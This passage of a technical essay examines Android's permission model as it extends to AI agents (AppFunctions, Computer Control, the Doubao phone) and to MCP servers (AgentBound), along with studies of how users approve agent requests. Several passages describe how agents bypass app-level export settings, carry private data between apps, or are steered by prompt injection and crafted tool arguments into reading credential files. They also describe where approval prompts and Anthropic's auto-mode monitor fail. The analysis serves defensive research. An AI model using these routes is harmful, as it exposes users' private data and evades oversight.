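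Bosu, Liu and colleagues (2017), in *Collusive Data Leak and More*, searched for suspicious pairs among 100,206 of the most downloaded apps on Google Play. Analysing every possible pair together would have taken far too long, so their tool, DIALDroid, analysed each app once. It recorded what sensitive data the app put into intents and what the app did with data it received in them, then matched senders with receivers in a database. It found 16,712 pairs in which sensitive data could pass from one app to another that lacked permission to access it, and then leave the second app.

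Only 33 apps were the senders in these pairs, which makes the number less alarming. A prayer-time app, for example, shared the user's location through an ordinary "send" intent, which 1,540 other apps could have received. DIALDroid also counted writing to the phone's log as a leak. When Bosu and colleagues counted only data that could leave the phone by internet or text message, 325 pairs remained.

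Bosu and colleagues describe one pair of apps in which an app for paraglider pilots put the pilot's location into a text message. A messaging app without the location permission could then send it. A pilot may have wanted this. The researchers couldn't determine whether the developers of any pair had planned a leak, and the permissions alone don't show intent either. Android checks each call separately and allows every call in a pair like this.

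### What Android adopted and what it left to developers

Android doesn't automatically reduce a deputy's permissions when another app calls it, but since Android 12 it has offered developers something similar to Quire's call chain. Android Developers' *AttributionSource* gives the example of a speech recognizer that uses the microphone on behalf of another app. The recognizer can declare that the data will go to that app, and Android checks that both apps have the microphone permission before releasing any sound.

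The app in the middle has to set this up. If the recognizer's developer forgets, Android checks only the recognizer, as it did in 2011. Quire proposed passing the chain along by default and letting developers drop it, whereas Android includes the chain only if a developer adds it. Developers can also write their own checks on callers, but InfoQ (2025) describes ignoring the result of such a check as a common mistake.

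Flaws of this kind are still easy to find. Diallo, Diop and colleagues (2025), in *Security Evaluation of Android Apps in Budget African Mobile Devices*, analysed 1,544 apps pre-installed on seven cheap phones. They found that 249 of the apps (16%) had a component that gave other apps access to sensitive data without requiring a permission. Their tool looked for permissions in the manifest, so the total may include components that check their callers in code.

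Google's own apps have problems too. In *A Systematic Study of Security Enforcement at Android Inter-Component Boundaries*, Christan (2026) tested more than 30 packages from Google and the Android Open Source Project on a phone running Android 17, using apps that held only the permissions Android grants automatically. In 97 of 120 evaluations, the phone's protection differed from what Christan expected. Many of these differences were deliberate design choices or minor problems, but tests on the phone confirmed 54 as security gaps. Christan classes seven of the 97 as confused deputies. These numbers don't show how common such flaws are, because Christan chose to test places where they seemed likely.

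Protections worked in 4 of 14 services and 8 of 29 content providers, which are databases that apps can share, but in none of the 27 screens or 11 broadcast receivers. These figures exclude 11 evaluations of components that Christan picked as examples of good security. Christan notes that services can identify their callers through Binder and that Android supplies ready-made checks for content providers, whereas a screen often can't identify the app that opened it. The comparison isn't controlled, but it suggests that developers protect components more often when Android makes it easy.

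## How Android 16 and 17 let AI agents operate apps

Google offers AI agents two ways to operate Android apps. With AppFunctions, an app's developer writes functions for agents to call. With Computer Control, an agent looks at screenshots of an app and taps its buttons, which requires no work from the app's developer.

Google presented both methods, function calls and screen tapping, in *The Intelligent OS* (McCullough, February 2026). In one example, a Galaxy S26 owner asks Gemini, Google's assistant, for pictures of a cat. Gemini calls a function in Samsung's Gallery app and shows the photos in its own window. Screen tapping began as a preview on Galaxy S26 phones and some Pixel 10 models, for selected food delivery, grocery and ride apps in the US and Korea.

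AppFunctions keep most of Android's older model, in which developers declare what others may call and Android checks each caller. Computer Control also has permissions and a user dialog, but it bypasses most of what developers declare in their manifests.

### Declaring a function

Suppose the developer of the notes app wants agents to be able to search a user's notes. The developer writes a function, marks it for use by agents, and describes it in a comment:

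```kotlin
/**
 * Search the user's notes for a word or phrase.
 *
 * @param text What to look for.
 * @return The notes that contain the text.
 */
@AppFunctionDeclaration(isDescribedByKDoc = true)
suspend fun searchNotes(text: String): List<Note>
```

Google's library turns such declarations into an XML file, which Android uses to index the functions. An agent searches the index, and its model picks a function based on the descriptions, much as it would pick a tool on an MCP server. According to Android Developers, an app can also include general advice on using its functions together.

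The functions usually run in a service inside the app. The manifest marks this service as exported, which would normally let any app call it, but also requires a permission that only the Android system holds. Agents therefore have to send each request to Android, which checks it and then calls the app. This spares developers from writing their own checks on callers, which Felt and colleagues found they rarely did.

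Android 17 added functions that exist only while the app is in a certain state, such as showing a particular screen. The notes app could use one to return the note the user is reading. The app must still declare the function in its XML file, and according to Android Developers' *AppFunctionManager*, Android rejects any function that the file doesn't list. An app's set of possible functions is therefore about as fixed as its manifest, whereas an MCP server can add new tools while running.

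After declaring functions, a developer must also register the app with Google to make them available to Gemini. Until the registration is published, only the developer's chosen testers can use the functions through Gemini.

### The checks on a call

utzcoz, who analysed Android's published source code in March 2026, traced what happens when an agent requests a function. Android refuses the call unless all of the following are true:

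1. The caller's user ID belongs to the app that the request names as its sender.
2. No company administrator has blocked the call.
3. The caller holds a permission named `EXECUTE_APP_FUNCTIONS`.
4. The caller is on the allowlist, the phone's list of approved agents.
5. The caller has a grant to use this particular app.
6. The function is switched on. Developers can switch off each function separately.

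The code checks the permission, the allowlist and the grant in a single step. If the call passes, Android starts the app's service, hands over the request, returns the result to the agent and records the call. The result can include URI grants, such as grants for three photos in a gallery app.

Each allowlist entry combines an app's name with its developer's certificate. The allowlist consists of a fixed entry for Android's command-line tool, entries from an updatable configuration list, and entries from a setting that programmers can change from a connected computer. On an ordinary user's phone, an agent will normally work only if whoever maintains the configuration list has approved it. Apps that aren't on the allowlist also can't look up other apps' functions, because MingWei (2025) changed Android's search index in *Update AppSearch visibility for EXECUTE_APP_FUNCTIONS permission*.

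AppFunctions follow Mayrhofer and colleagues' rule of three-way consent. The developer declares the function, the platform approves the agent, and the user decides whether that agent may use that app. However, a phone can come with some pairs of agents and apps already approved, and an administrator can allow or deny a pair. The user's choice overrides the administrator's.

Each grant covers a pair of apps, not individual functions. If a user lets Gemini search a mail app that also offers a function for sending messages, Gemini may call that function too. The `EXECUTE_APP_FUNCTIONS` permission is broader still and covers every function in every app. Google can't rate its risk as it rated the camera permission's, because it covers both reading a recipe and paying a bill.

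### A normal permission with a closed list

Google's descriptions of `EXECUTE_APP_FUNCTIONS` are hard to reconcile. In answers to developers' questions, Android Developers calls it a privileged permission that Android grants only to authorized system assistants. But *Manifest.permission*, the site's reference list of all permissions, gives its protection level as normal, so any app that requests it gets it.

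In an early version, only preinstalled apps with the assistant role could hold the EXECUTE_APP_FUNCTIONS permission, according to a copy of Android's code kept by the e Foundation. Google then opened it to all privileged system apps. In *Update the protection level of EXECUTE_APP_FUNCTIONS permission*, MingWei later changed the protection level to normal, but required the app to be on the device's allowlist and let the user approve or deny its access. The change applies only when a feature flag is on, so a phone with the flag off still uses the privileged level.

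The reference list matches the newer version, so the protection level Google now documents is normal. It also includes a note that Android checks the allowlist when an app makes a call. In practice, the description in Google's answers is still roughly right, since few apps other than approved assistants can use the permission. The game from the earlier example would get the permission if it requested it, but every call it made to another app's functions would fail.

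An outsider can therefore learn very little from the permission. The game's manifest lists a permission to act on the user's behalf inside other apps, but a reviewer would have to check the phone's allowlist to learn that the game can't do so. The allowlist can also change after the review, with no change to the game.

### The app doesn't learn who is calling

Android used to send the app the agent's name and certificate with each request, so the app could refuse some callers, as it can when another app calls it directly through Binder.

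From Android 17, the name is always empty and the certificate information is always unknown, according to Android Developers' *android.app.appfunctions*. Google also strongly recommends that a function behave the same way for every caller, so users get a predictable experience.

The developer of the notes app therefore can't let one agent delete notes and allow another only to search them. If the app offers a delete function, any approved agent that has a grant for the app can call it. A developer who trusts only some of those agents can leave the function out, switch it off for everyone, or build a confirmation screen into the app. In an early version of the permission's description, an app could accept only callers with a second permission for trusted agents. A later description, which MingWei replaced, doesn't mention this option.

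One reasonable argument for the change is that Android has already checked the agent, in one place and with the same rules for every app. If thousands of developers each wrote their own checks, many would get them wrong. Anonymous calls also make it harder for an app to accept its owner's preferred assistant and reject a competitor's. But the mail app's developer probably knows better than Google how much damage a careless agent could do in a mailbox, and Android 17 removes the information the developer would need to act on that knowledge.

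The missing name would have been of limited use anyway, because it would have identified Gemini without showing whether Gemini was following the user's request or a line in an email it had just read.

### Always allow, by default

A later update to Android 17, which Google labels version 37.2, adds a way to ask users for consent while an agent is working. The agent opens a session and names the apps it wants to use. If Android requires consent, the agent has to open a consent screen. Android Developers' *AppInteractionSession* gives the example of an agent that needs the same app twice during one conversation. Android can remember the user's consent for the session, so the agent doesn't have to ask again. The session closes automatically after a maximum time.

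This saves the user from repeated dialogs, but the user agrees before the agent has read anything. If the agent opens the mail app twice, the same consent covers both calls, even if the second is a response to something the agent found during the first.

Agents that haven't adopted this system get more access by default. According to Android Developers, if an app doesn't declare that it supports "runtime user control", Android gives the caller "always allow" access when someone installs the package, though the user can restrict or block this in the settings. Google's wording is slightly ambiguous, but the agent seems to be the app that must declare this, because it has to know how to open the consent screen.

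Google's reason is compatibility, since an older agent would stop working if Android suddenly expected it to ask for consent. Android has often handled older apps in this way. However, this approach contradicts Saltzer and Schroeder's advice to deny access by default. It also discourages developers from doing the extra work to ask for consent, because some users will refuse, and most will probably never notice the access an agent gets if its developer does nothing. Google says that a future version of Android will ignore the declaration. Until then, the allowlist limits the damage, since only approved agents can benefit from the default.

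### What Android records

Android keeps a history of AppFunction calls for seven days. In the code that utzcoz analysed, each entry contains the agent, the app, the time and the length of the call. It also has fields for whether the call came from a user's request or a schedule, an identifier that groups calls from one conversation, and a link back to that conversation. The agent fills in these three fields, so they are only as reliable as the agent.

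utzcoz lists no field for the name of the function or for its arguments. The history could therefore show that Gemini used the notes app at ten past three, but not whether it searched the notes or deleted them all.

In *Android's Agentic Future*, Google promises a page in the phone's privacy dashboard that shows which assistants were active in the last 24 hours and which apps they used, and a separate page for controlling access. In *Android 17 QPR2 Beta 4 puts AI agents under supervision*, Mehta (2026) reports finding a new "Agents" entry in the privacy settings of a test version in August 2026. The entry is meant to list agents that can read information or act within apps, but it was still empty on the test phone. Android Developers' *AppInteractionManager* describes settings screens where a user can look up all the apps that one agent may use, or all the agents that may use one app.

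The second kind of screen is quite useful to someone who wants to know whether an agent can open their bank's app. Neither screen would help them much to work out later what an agent did there.

### The recipe in Lisa's email

The noodle recipe request, Google's own example, spans two apps. The mail app offers a function named `searchEmails`, which takes a search term and returns summaries of the matching emails. The shopping app offers `addItemsToShoppingList`, which takes a list of items. If Gemini handles the request, it makes two calls, and Android checks each of them:

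| Check | Searching the email | Adding the ingredients |
|---|---|---|
| Identity | The caller really is Gemini | Same |
| Company policy | No administrator has blocked the call | Same |
| Permission | Gemini holds `EXECUTE_APP_FUNCTIONS` | Same |
| Allowlist | Gemini is an approved agent | Same |
| Grant | Gemini may use the mail app | Gemini may use the shopping app |
| Enabled state | `searchEmails` is on | `addItemsToShoppingList` is on |

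The mail app receives a search term from a caller it can't identify and returns the text it finds. Gemini's model then extracts the ingredients from this text, a step Android isn't involved in. Android checks the second call separately, and the check doesn't take into account that the items came from an email or that Gemini made the first call.

Suppose the user shares the shopping list with a flatmate, and Lisa's email also mentions that she is about to leave her husband. If the model mistakenly copied that sentence into the list along with the noodles, both columns of the table would stay the same. `addItemsToShoppingList` takes a list of text items, and the sentence is a valid item.

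Android has some of the information it would need to connect the two calls. Gemini can label both with the same conversation identifier, and in version 37.2 it can open one session for both apps. But the identifier goes into the history, and the session tracks consent. Neither records what data came out of the mail app, so neither can stop that data from going into the shopping app. The mail app's developer can't prevent this either, because the app has no way to attach a condition that Android would enforce, such as "only for the user", to the text it returns.

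### Computer Control

Many apps offer no functions to agents, or lack the one a task needs. Computer Control lets an agent use these apps through their screens. Android reserves it for preinstalled assistants that hold the privileged `ACCESS_COMPUTER_CONTROL` permission.

The assistant first requests a session for up to six apps, to use one after another. According to Android Developers' *Android Computer Control*, only one session can be active at a time, and a system dialog asks the user to let the assistant automate the apps. If the user agrees, Android runs them on a virtual display, a screen that exists only in software, so the user can do something else on the real one. The assistant takes a screenshot, works out where to tap, swipe or type, does so, and takes another screenshot to see what happened. In the code that utzcoz read, Android waited two seconds after a tap and three after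 opening an app before treating the screen as settled, so an order with many steps could take a while.

The user can watch the assistant work and take over at any point. The assistant can also hand control to the user, for example to confirm a payment. Google says a notification that the user can't dismiss stays on the screen while Gemini is automating an app.

Android also restricts what the assistant can operate. utzcoz found a strict mode that blocks every app not named in the session. In either mode, the assistant can't operate the part of Android that shows permission dialogs, so it can't use a session to tap "Allow" for the user. A session can't start while the phone is locked. According to Android Developers' *What's new for enterprise in Android 17*, automation doesn't work inside work profiles, which keep company apps separate on an employee's phone. Bayton's *Android 17 enterprise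 features* notes that automation is allowed on fully company-managed phones unless an administrator turns it off.

### What a tap can reach

These limits all apply to whole apps. Inside an app that the user has approved, the developer's export settings have almost no effect on what an assistant can do. An assistant can open the notes app's locked screen, for example, even though that screen isn't exported:

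1. It opens the notes app at its main screen.
2. It finds the "Locked notes" button in a screenshot and taps it.
3. The notes app handles the tap as if it came from a finger, and sends an explicit intent to its own locked screen.
4. Android opens the screen, because the sender and the receiver are the same app.

Android has applied the export rule correctly, since the intent came from the notes app. The assistant caused the app to send it, much as a malicious app once caused Android's Settings app to switch on the GPS. Unlike Settings, the notes app wasn't careless, because an app has to respond to taps on its own buttons and its developer reasonably assumed that a person would be tapping them. Only a check that the assistant can't pass by tapping or typing, such as a fingerprint, would stop it.

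The grant therefore covers everything a user could do in the app by hand. Someone who lets an assistant reorder groceries also lets it change the delivery address or close the account, if the app has buttons for these. With AppFunctions, a grant also covers more than one function, but the developer has chosen which functions to offer. Computer Control doesn't involve the developer. Google tells developers that an assistant can use their app without any changes, and its documentation describes no setting for keeping assistants out.

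Android also can't easily distinguish the taps that matter, because a tap on "Pay" and a tap on "Back" are both touches at a position on the screen. Google says that Gemini "is designed to" ask the user before it makes a purchase, so this protection depends on Gemini recognizing a purchase. An app's own confirmation step adds little protection, because the assistant can tap the confirmation button too.

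A session can also carry data from one app to another. *Who Asked for My Data?* (Wu, Peng and colleagues, 2026) tested agents that operate phones through the screen and found that malicious apps could use the agents to obtain private data from other apps, even though the phones' isolation and permission checks worked as designed.

### The Doubao phone

ByteDance, the company behind TikTok, tried a broader version of this before Google did. In December 2025 it released a test version of an assistant, based on its Doubao chatbot, on the Nubia M153 phone. According to *Turing Test on Screen* (2026), the assistant combined a model that could interpret screenshots with `INJECT_EVENTS`, a system permission for simulating taps. A user could ask it to open WeChat, China's main messaging app, and tell their wife they would be home in 20 minutes.

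`INJECT_EVENTS` isn't limited to particular apps. Computer Control is narrower, since it works only with the apps in a session and shows the user a dialog. In both cases, the phone maker grants the power and app makers have no say.

App makers soon responded anyway. *突发！豆包想操纵手机，被腾讯和阿里们集体“封杀”* (符, 2026) gives a day-by-day account. The phone went on sale on December 1. From the next day, some people who had used the assistant in WeChat were logged out, with a warning about an unusual login environment. ByteDance withdrew the WeChat feature on December 3. Users then reported trouble logging in to the shopping app Taobao and other apps, and some banking apps showed risk warnings. On December 5, ByteDance announced limits on what the assistant could do in financial apps and games, and proposed working out common rules with app makers.

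WeChat said that it had taken no special action and that the assistant might have triggered its existing security controls. This is plausible because apps that face a lot of fraud try to detect software that imitates a user, as an assistant does when it taps buttons. These controls gave the apps a crude way to refuse the assistant, which the phone's permission system did not let them do.

In its second attempt, the consumer version of the assistant in September 2026, ByteDance introduced the Screen Automation Execution Protocol, which lets developers state whether agents may operate their app, down to individual pages and actions. This is similar to Android's export setting, but for taps. The notes app could allow an agent to use its search page and keep it away from the locked notes. However, the protocol relies on Doubao to honour these choices. ByteDance has promised that Doubao will not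 operate apps that explicitly refuse, but that promise does not cover apps whose developers have never replied.

By the middle of October, 151 apps had rejected Doubao, according to Yicai Global's *WeChat, Taobao, Honor of Kings Among 151 Apps to Reject Doubao* (2026). They included WeChat, Taobao, the payment app Alipay, several banks, and the AI apps DeepSeek and Kimi. Tencent, which owns WeChat, and its affiliates accounted for 65 of them.

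The list gives no reasons, but security probably isn't the only one. 符 points out that Tencent and Taobao's owner, Alibaba, are building their own agents, and that a shopper who asks Doubao for a phone may never see the products Taobao wants to promote. Tencent doesn't oppose all agents, though. In June 2026 WeChat began letting developers of the small programs that run inside it open their services to AI, and it has worked with the phone maker Honor and others so their assistants can call some WeChat functions with authorization.

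Tencent thus wants to offer functions to some agents and refuse others. On Android 17, an app can't do this through AppFunctions because it can no longer identify the calling agent. If large app makers elsewhere want the same choice, some may offer no functions. Google's assistant would have to use their apps by tapping, which gives the developer even less control.

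## Whether users can judge permission requests

The user must approve a dialog before an agent can use Computer Control, and may have to approve one before an agent can call AppFunctions. Both dialogs rely on the last of the six assumptions, that the person tapping "Allow" can judge the request. Researchers have been testing this assumption on Android since 2011, with discouraging results.

### The list before installation

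In 2011, the last page before installing an app from Google's store listed the permissions the app requested. The user could accept them all or cancel.

Felt, Ha and colleagues (2012), in *Android Permissions*, asked 308 Android users what they had looked at before they last installed an app, and 17.5% mentioned permissions. People may exaggerate how careful they are, so the researchers also watched 25 people install apps on their own phones, without telling them that the study was about security. Of the 24 who had previously installed an app without help, four looked at the permissions, ten didn't look but knew about them, and ten had never noticed them.

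The survey included a quiz in which each person saw three permission warnings and picked what each one allowed. Only 8 of 302 people got all three right. An answer counted as right only if it included every correct option and no wrong ones. About half of all answers included at least one correct option. Android's wording caused some of the errors. Permission to place phone calls appeared under the heading "Services that cost you money", and while 35% of people knew it let an app make calls, 32% thought it let the app charge their credit card.

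The researchers themselves wrongly assumed in one question that apps needed permission to see the photo library. They then discovered that any app could view and edit it without permission.

Felt and colleagues still saw some value in the warnings. About a fifth of the people they watched knew about permissions and understood them fairly well. These people could warn others by writing reviews, which 22 of the 25 participants read before installing. That works for apps because everyone who installs the same app sees the same permissions. An agent's requests depend on one user's task, so nobody can have reviewed them beforehand.

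### Asking while the app runs

Android 6, released in 2015, replaced the list with dialogs that appear when an app first needs a dangerous permission. Someone who has just tapped a camera button can usually guess why the app needs the camera. If the user agreed, the permission lasted until they withdrew it in the settings.

A user's one answer to a permission request had to cover many later uses. For *Android Permissions Remystified* (2015), Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues gave 36 people phones with a modified version of Android for a week. The phones logged 27 million permission checks, or more than 100,000 per person per day. In 75% of checks, the user had no sign that the app was running, and in 60% the screen was off. Many checks were trivial, such as whether the phone was online. But about once every 20 seconds, an app used one of the 12 permissions that the researchers considered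 sensitive, which is far too often to ask the user each time.

At the end of the week, participants saw screenshots of what they had been doing when apps used these permissions. They would have blocked 149 of 423 uses (35%), most often because the app didn't seem to need the data. They wanted to block 43% of uses by apps in the background, compared with 29% by apps on the screen. Some were probably wrong about what an app needed, but their answers show that agreeing to a use while the app is on the screen doesn't imply agreeing to the same use later. *The Feasibility of Dynamically Granted Permissions* (2017) proposes a machine-learning model that infers when the circumstances have changed, so that the phone prompts the user again only then.

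### How people answer agents

Most of the evidence on agents comes from programmers, whose coding agents constantly ask for permission. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, used to ask by default before running a command or changing a file. Users accepted 93% of these requests, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. A later Anthropic post, *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), puts the figure at 97%.

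A high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless, because most requests are harmless and should be approved. Anthropic notes that users reject 39% of the plans Claude shows them, but they may do so simply because they want a different design.

Anthropic also ran an experiment, which is better evidence. It hired 1,053 professional testers for what they thought was a coding study. Partway through each session, one permission request showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

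The testers had little to lose, since they weren't working on their own projects, and Anthropic was arguing for a product that replaces these requests. Both are reasons to doubt that 13.6% applies to ordinary work. Low stakes don't easily explain the decline, though, because the stakes were the same throughout a session.

Programmers describe similar habits. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers and found that 64% often approved at least one type of agent action without close review. Even among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the code their agents wrote, 61% did. Developers who knew of security or privacy problems with agents were more likely to approve actions this way (70%) than those who didn't (43%), even after the researchers adjusted for how much they used agents.

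Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 practitioners and surveyed 115. Of the 107 who answered questions about permissions, 48% said they read requests carefully, 34% skimmed them and 21% approved by default. A third admitted they had become less careful over time. One interviewee complained that having to click something every ten seconds defeated the purpose of using an agent.

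People outside the software industry also approve actions they didn't ask for. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 such people supervise a simulated assistant through a day of email and travel. The assistant attempted 18 actions, 11 of which the task required. The other seven went beyond the task, and included reading private messages and buying a $25 airport lounge pass. Participants who had to decide on every action approved 40% of the actions that went beyond the task.

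Some participants may have wanted the extra actions. For example, 88% let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight, which would do little harm. Without that call, the share falls to 32%. But a third of these participants also let the assistant permanently delete an old work timesheet.

### Why an agent's requests are harder to judge

An Android dialog usually interrupts something the user is doing, but an agent's request often arrives after the user has turned to other work, since much of the point of using an agent is not having to watch it. The user then has to remember the task and work out how far the agent has got. In the Android field study, people who saw a screenshot correctly guessed which permission an app was using 44% of the time when the app was on the screen and 29% when it was in the background.

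The request may also reveal little about what will happen. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of `python3 setup.py`, a routine-looking command that runs whatever code is in `setup.py`. Of the 290 reports it analyses, 31 involved an approval request that didn't give the user enough information. In 80 reports, including some of those 31, users had turned on automatic approval.

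Even a clear permission request can be impossible to judge on its own. Suppose an assistant asks to read Lisa's email. Granting access is fine if the assistant then adds noodles to a shopping list, but not if it posts her message publicly, and the user has to answer before the model has chosen its next step. Salerno and colleagues found that 98% of the practitioners they surveyed were more willing to grant read-only access than other kinds. An assistant with read-only access can't delete anything, but prompt injections reach the model through what it reads.

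Android could tolerate inattentive users because their approval was only one of its safeguards. The game in the earlier example can't get the notes app's `SYNC` permission, no matter how carelessly the user approves requests. When a coding agent asks to run a command, the user's approval may be the only safeguard.

### How many harmful requests get through

A small calculation with invented numbers shows why so many requests are a problem. Suppose someone gives an agent 200 tasks in a year, each with 50 permission requests. One request in 1,000 is harmful, and the user notices a harmful request 15% of the time. If $N$ is the number of requests, $h$ the harmful share and $q$ the chance of noticing, then the expected number of harmful approvals is

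$$N \times h \times (1-q) = 10{,}000 \times 0.001 \times 0.85 = 8.5$$

The user stops only 1.5 of the ten harmful actions. Approving every request without reading it would be the right decision 99.9% of the time, so the habit is easy to acquire.

Now suppose a filter approves most requests automatically and shows the user only 2,000 of them. The filter isn't perfect, so it lets two of the ten harmful actions through and passes on the other eight. The outcome depends on how much better the user judges the shorter list:

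| What the user sees | Chance of noticing | Harmful actions stopped | Harmful actions that go ahead |
|---|---|---|---|
| All 10,000 requests | 15% | 1.5 | 8.5 |
| 2,000 requests | 17% | 1.4 | 8.6 |
| 2,000 requests | 50% | 4 | 6 |

If the user's attention improves only slightly, they are worse off than before, because the filter's own mistakes slightly outweigh the benefit. The 17% in the table is the share of dangerous commands that Anthropic's testers refused early in a session. If real users are similar, reducing their fatigue won't help much unless the requests also become easier to judge.

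*Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) models reviewers whose attention declines with each request. In this model, sending every action to a person can be less safe than sending fewer if reviewers get much worse as they tire. The study applied the model to scored actions and had no human participants.

### Letting a model answer

Another option is to predict what the user would say. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, asked 205 people to train an imaginary assistant by deciding which data it could share with tools, such as whether it could give a travel site their passport number. The choices were to share always, share once, refuse once or never share. Some questions included data that the tool didn't need. When participants mistakenly thought such data was necessary, they let the assistant share it about 78% of the time.

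The researchers then built a predictor. It gives a language model a person's earlier decisions, some details about them, and recommendations based on people who made similar choices. It predicted 85.1% of decisions correctly, with two kinds of error:

- It would have shared 15.2% of the data that people refused to share.
- It would have withheld 14.8% of the data that people agreed to share.

Wrongly allowing a request is worse than wrongly denying one, because an agent can ask again for a passport number it didn't get, but nobody can take back one it has sent. Keeping only the predictor's most confident answers raised accuracy to 94.4%, but these covered just 25.9% of requests, so the user would still have to decide the rest.

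The test used only "always" and "never" answers and left out one-time decisions, which are probably harder to predict. A perfect predictor would also copy its user's mistakes, including sharing data with a tool that doesn't need it.

In Anthropic's auto mode, a second model checks whether the user's instructions authorize an action, and blocks the action if it seems dangerous and unauthorized. This model sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not the tool results, so text injected into a web page or file does not reach it. In Anthropic's early tests, it wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary calls and missed 17% of 52 real cases in which Claude had done more than the user authorized. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the model correctly classified the action as dangerous but wrongly classified it as authorized.

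In the experiment with the 1,053 testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands. Anthropic made it the default on several Claude Code plans in August 2026, and in October announced the same change for most Claude apps on those plans. It still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

This moves a decision from the user to the platform, as Android's signature permissions do. But Android compares two certificates and gets the same answer every time, whereas auto mode relies on a model's interpretation of what the user meant. Users can also find it hard to see or change how such a model decides. Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, tried five commercial agents in May and June 2026. They found that users often had to choose between frequent requests and automatic review that offered little transparency or control.

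### Better requests and sandboxes

Yan tested whether people could avoid repeated requests by setting rules in advance. Some participants chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, which sent most decisions back to them. The rules reduced the average number of requests from 18 to 10.9, but these participants blocked only about 40% of the extra actions, compared with 60% for those who decided on everything. It isn't clear why, but perhaps setting the rules made them feel that the assistant was already under control. The day was also too short to cause much fatigue, so reducing the number of requests had little chance to help.

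There is some evidence for asking users to confirm an agent's work at points during a task instead of at the end. Salerno and colleagues describe a study by Zhou and colleagues in which 48 participants preferred this, but the preference doesn't show whether people catch more mistakes that way. In the survey of 203 developers, those who inspected line-by-line comparisons of code changes were less likely to approve several kinds of risky action, including destructive commands. These developers may be more careful in general, but a comparison also gives a reviewer something concrete to check.

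A sandbox, a closed-off environment that limits what an agent can reach, protects users even when they judge a request badly. In Salerno and colleagues' survey, 82% were more willing to grant permissions in a controlled environment, and some interviewees said they paid less attention to requests there. That is reasonable as long as the sandbox contains the damage. Anthropic considers sandboxing safe but laborious, because users must configure each new capability. It also says that giving the agent network access breaks the isolation. Neither group measured how much harm sandboxes prevent.

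Sandboxes suit coding agents because much of their work is changing files that a programmer can restore. An assistant that sends email and pays bills has to act outside a sandbox, where the user often can't undo a mistaken approval.

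## AgentBound: Android-style manifests for tool servers

Sandboxes protect users who approve requests carelessly, but someone has to configure each one, which Anthropic finds laborious. On Android, developers do much of this work in advance by listing the permissions their apps need. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) applies this arrangement to MCP servers. The developer ships each server with a manifest of the permissions it needs, the user approves particular folders and websites, and a sandbox blocks everything else.

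### What MCP servers can reach

An MCP server on the user's computer usually runs with all of the user's rights, like most desktop programs. A server that only tells the time could read the user's private keys, and the MCP specification leaves it to the host and the server's developer to prevent this. In *My Credentials, Please*, Huang, Tang and colleagues (2026) point out that approving a tool call doesn't restrict which files the server opens while handling it.

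Li, Li and colleagues (2025), in *We Urgently Need Privilege Management in MCP*, searched the source code of 2,562 servers for functions that use sensitive resources:

| Resource | Servers that use it | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Network | 1,438 | 56% |
| System functions, such as starting other programs | 1,237 | 48% |
| Files | 613 | 24% |
| Direct access to memory | 25 | 1% |

Many of these servers probably need the access. A search tool, for example, can't work without a network connection. The numbers measure how many servers use powerful functions, not how many have more access than they need.

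System functions appear in 45% of the servers with at most ten stars on GitHub, where users give stars to projects they like, and in 68% of those with 101 to 1,000, so choosing well-known servers wouldn't spare a user the risk. Li and colleagues conclude instead that less popular servers do riskier things. They report 1,837 sensitive calls for servers with at most ten stars and far fewer for popular ones. But those numbers add up to exactly 2,562, so they seem to count servers instead of calls, and most servers are unpopular.

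Excess access is harder to measure because it requires deciding what each server needs. Huang and colleagues sorted 4,806 servers by purpose and found 787 (16.4%) that could handle files although their category was unrelated to files. They treat this only as a rough signal, since a server that stores an agent's memory may legitimately need to save files.

They then ran selected servers and placed a fake credentials file outside the folders each tool needed. In 150 confirmed cases, an attacker who could influence a tool's arguments could make it exceed its proper scope, usually by returning the contents of the fake file. Anthropic's own Git server had such a flaw. Its tool for adding files to a code repository accepted files from outside the repository, and another tool then displayed their contents. Later versions reject such files.

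### Turning Android's list into a manifest

Bühler and colleagues needed a list of permissions that would suit any MCP server, so they collected 16 use cases for agents from 11 technical papers and noted which Android permissions an app would need for each. For example, an agent that looks things up online would need Android's internet permission.

Most MCP servers run on desktop computers, so the researchers compared their list of permissions with the privacy controls in macOS. They dropped permissions tied to phone hardware, such as body sensors, and merged precise and approximate location into one entry. They also added resources that matter on a desktop, such as the clipboard and environment variables, settings that often contain passwords for online services.

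In *Securing AI Agent Execution*, an earlier version of the paper, Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2025) described a shorter method for producing the same list. They started with Android's permissions and removed those that seemed irrelevant to agents, such as access to contacts and text messages. The later literature search therefore seems to have confirmed the list more than it shaped it.

| Group | Entries |
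|---|---|
| Files | Read, write, delete |
| System | Read environment variables, set environment variables, run commands, manage processes |
| Network | Connect to other computers, accept connections, use Bluetooth |
| Devices | Camera, microphone, speaker, screen capture |
| Other | Location, notifications, read clipboard, write clipboard |

AgentBound calls each entry a "capability", but the entries are named rights, like Android permissions, and not tickets that a holder can pass on. A manifest for a server that gives agents access to files could look like this:

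```json
{
  "description": "Lets an agent open and change files on this computer.",
  "capabilities": [
    "mcp.ac.filesystem.read",
    "mcp.ac.filesystem.write"
  ]
}
```

The list contains only resources of the computer, not actions such as sending an email or paying a bill. A dictionary server and a mail server that both work through a website would each need `mcp.ac.network.client`, the entry for connecting to other computers. Google gave Android's camera permission a single risk rating, but nobody could do that for `mcp.ac.network.client`, because its consequences depend on what the website at the other end does.

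### From a general entry to one folder

Suppose a programmer asks an agent to write documentation for some code. The agent uses one server to read and write files and another to fetch web pages. The manifests list file access and network access in general terms, and AgentBound turns these into specific grants before the servers start:

1. The agent asks for read access to the folder with the code, write access to the README file, and access to the website that documents a library the code uses.
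2. AgentBound compares these requests with the manifests. If the agent asked for environment variables, which neither manifest lists, AgentBound would stop.
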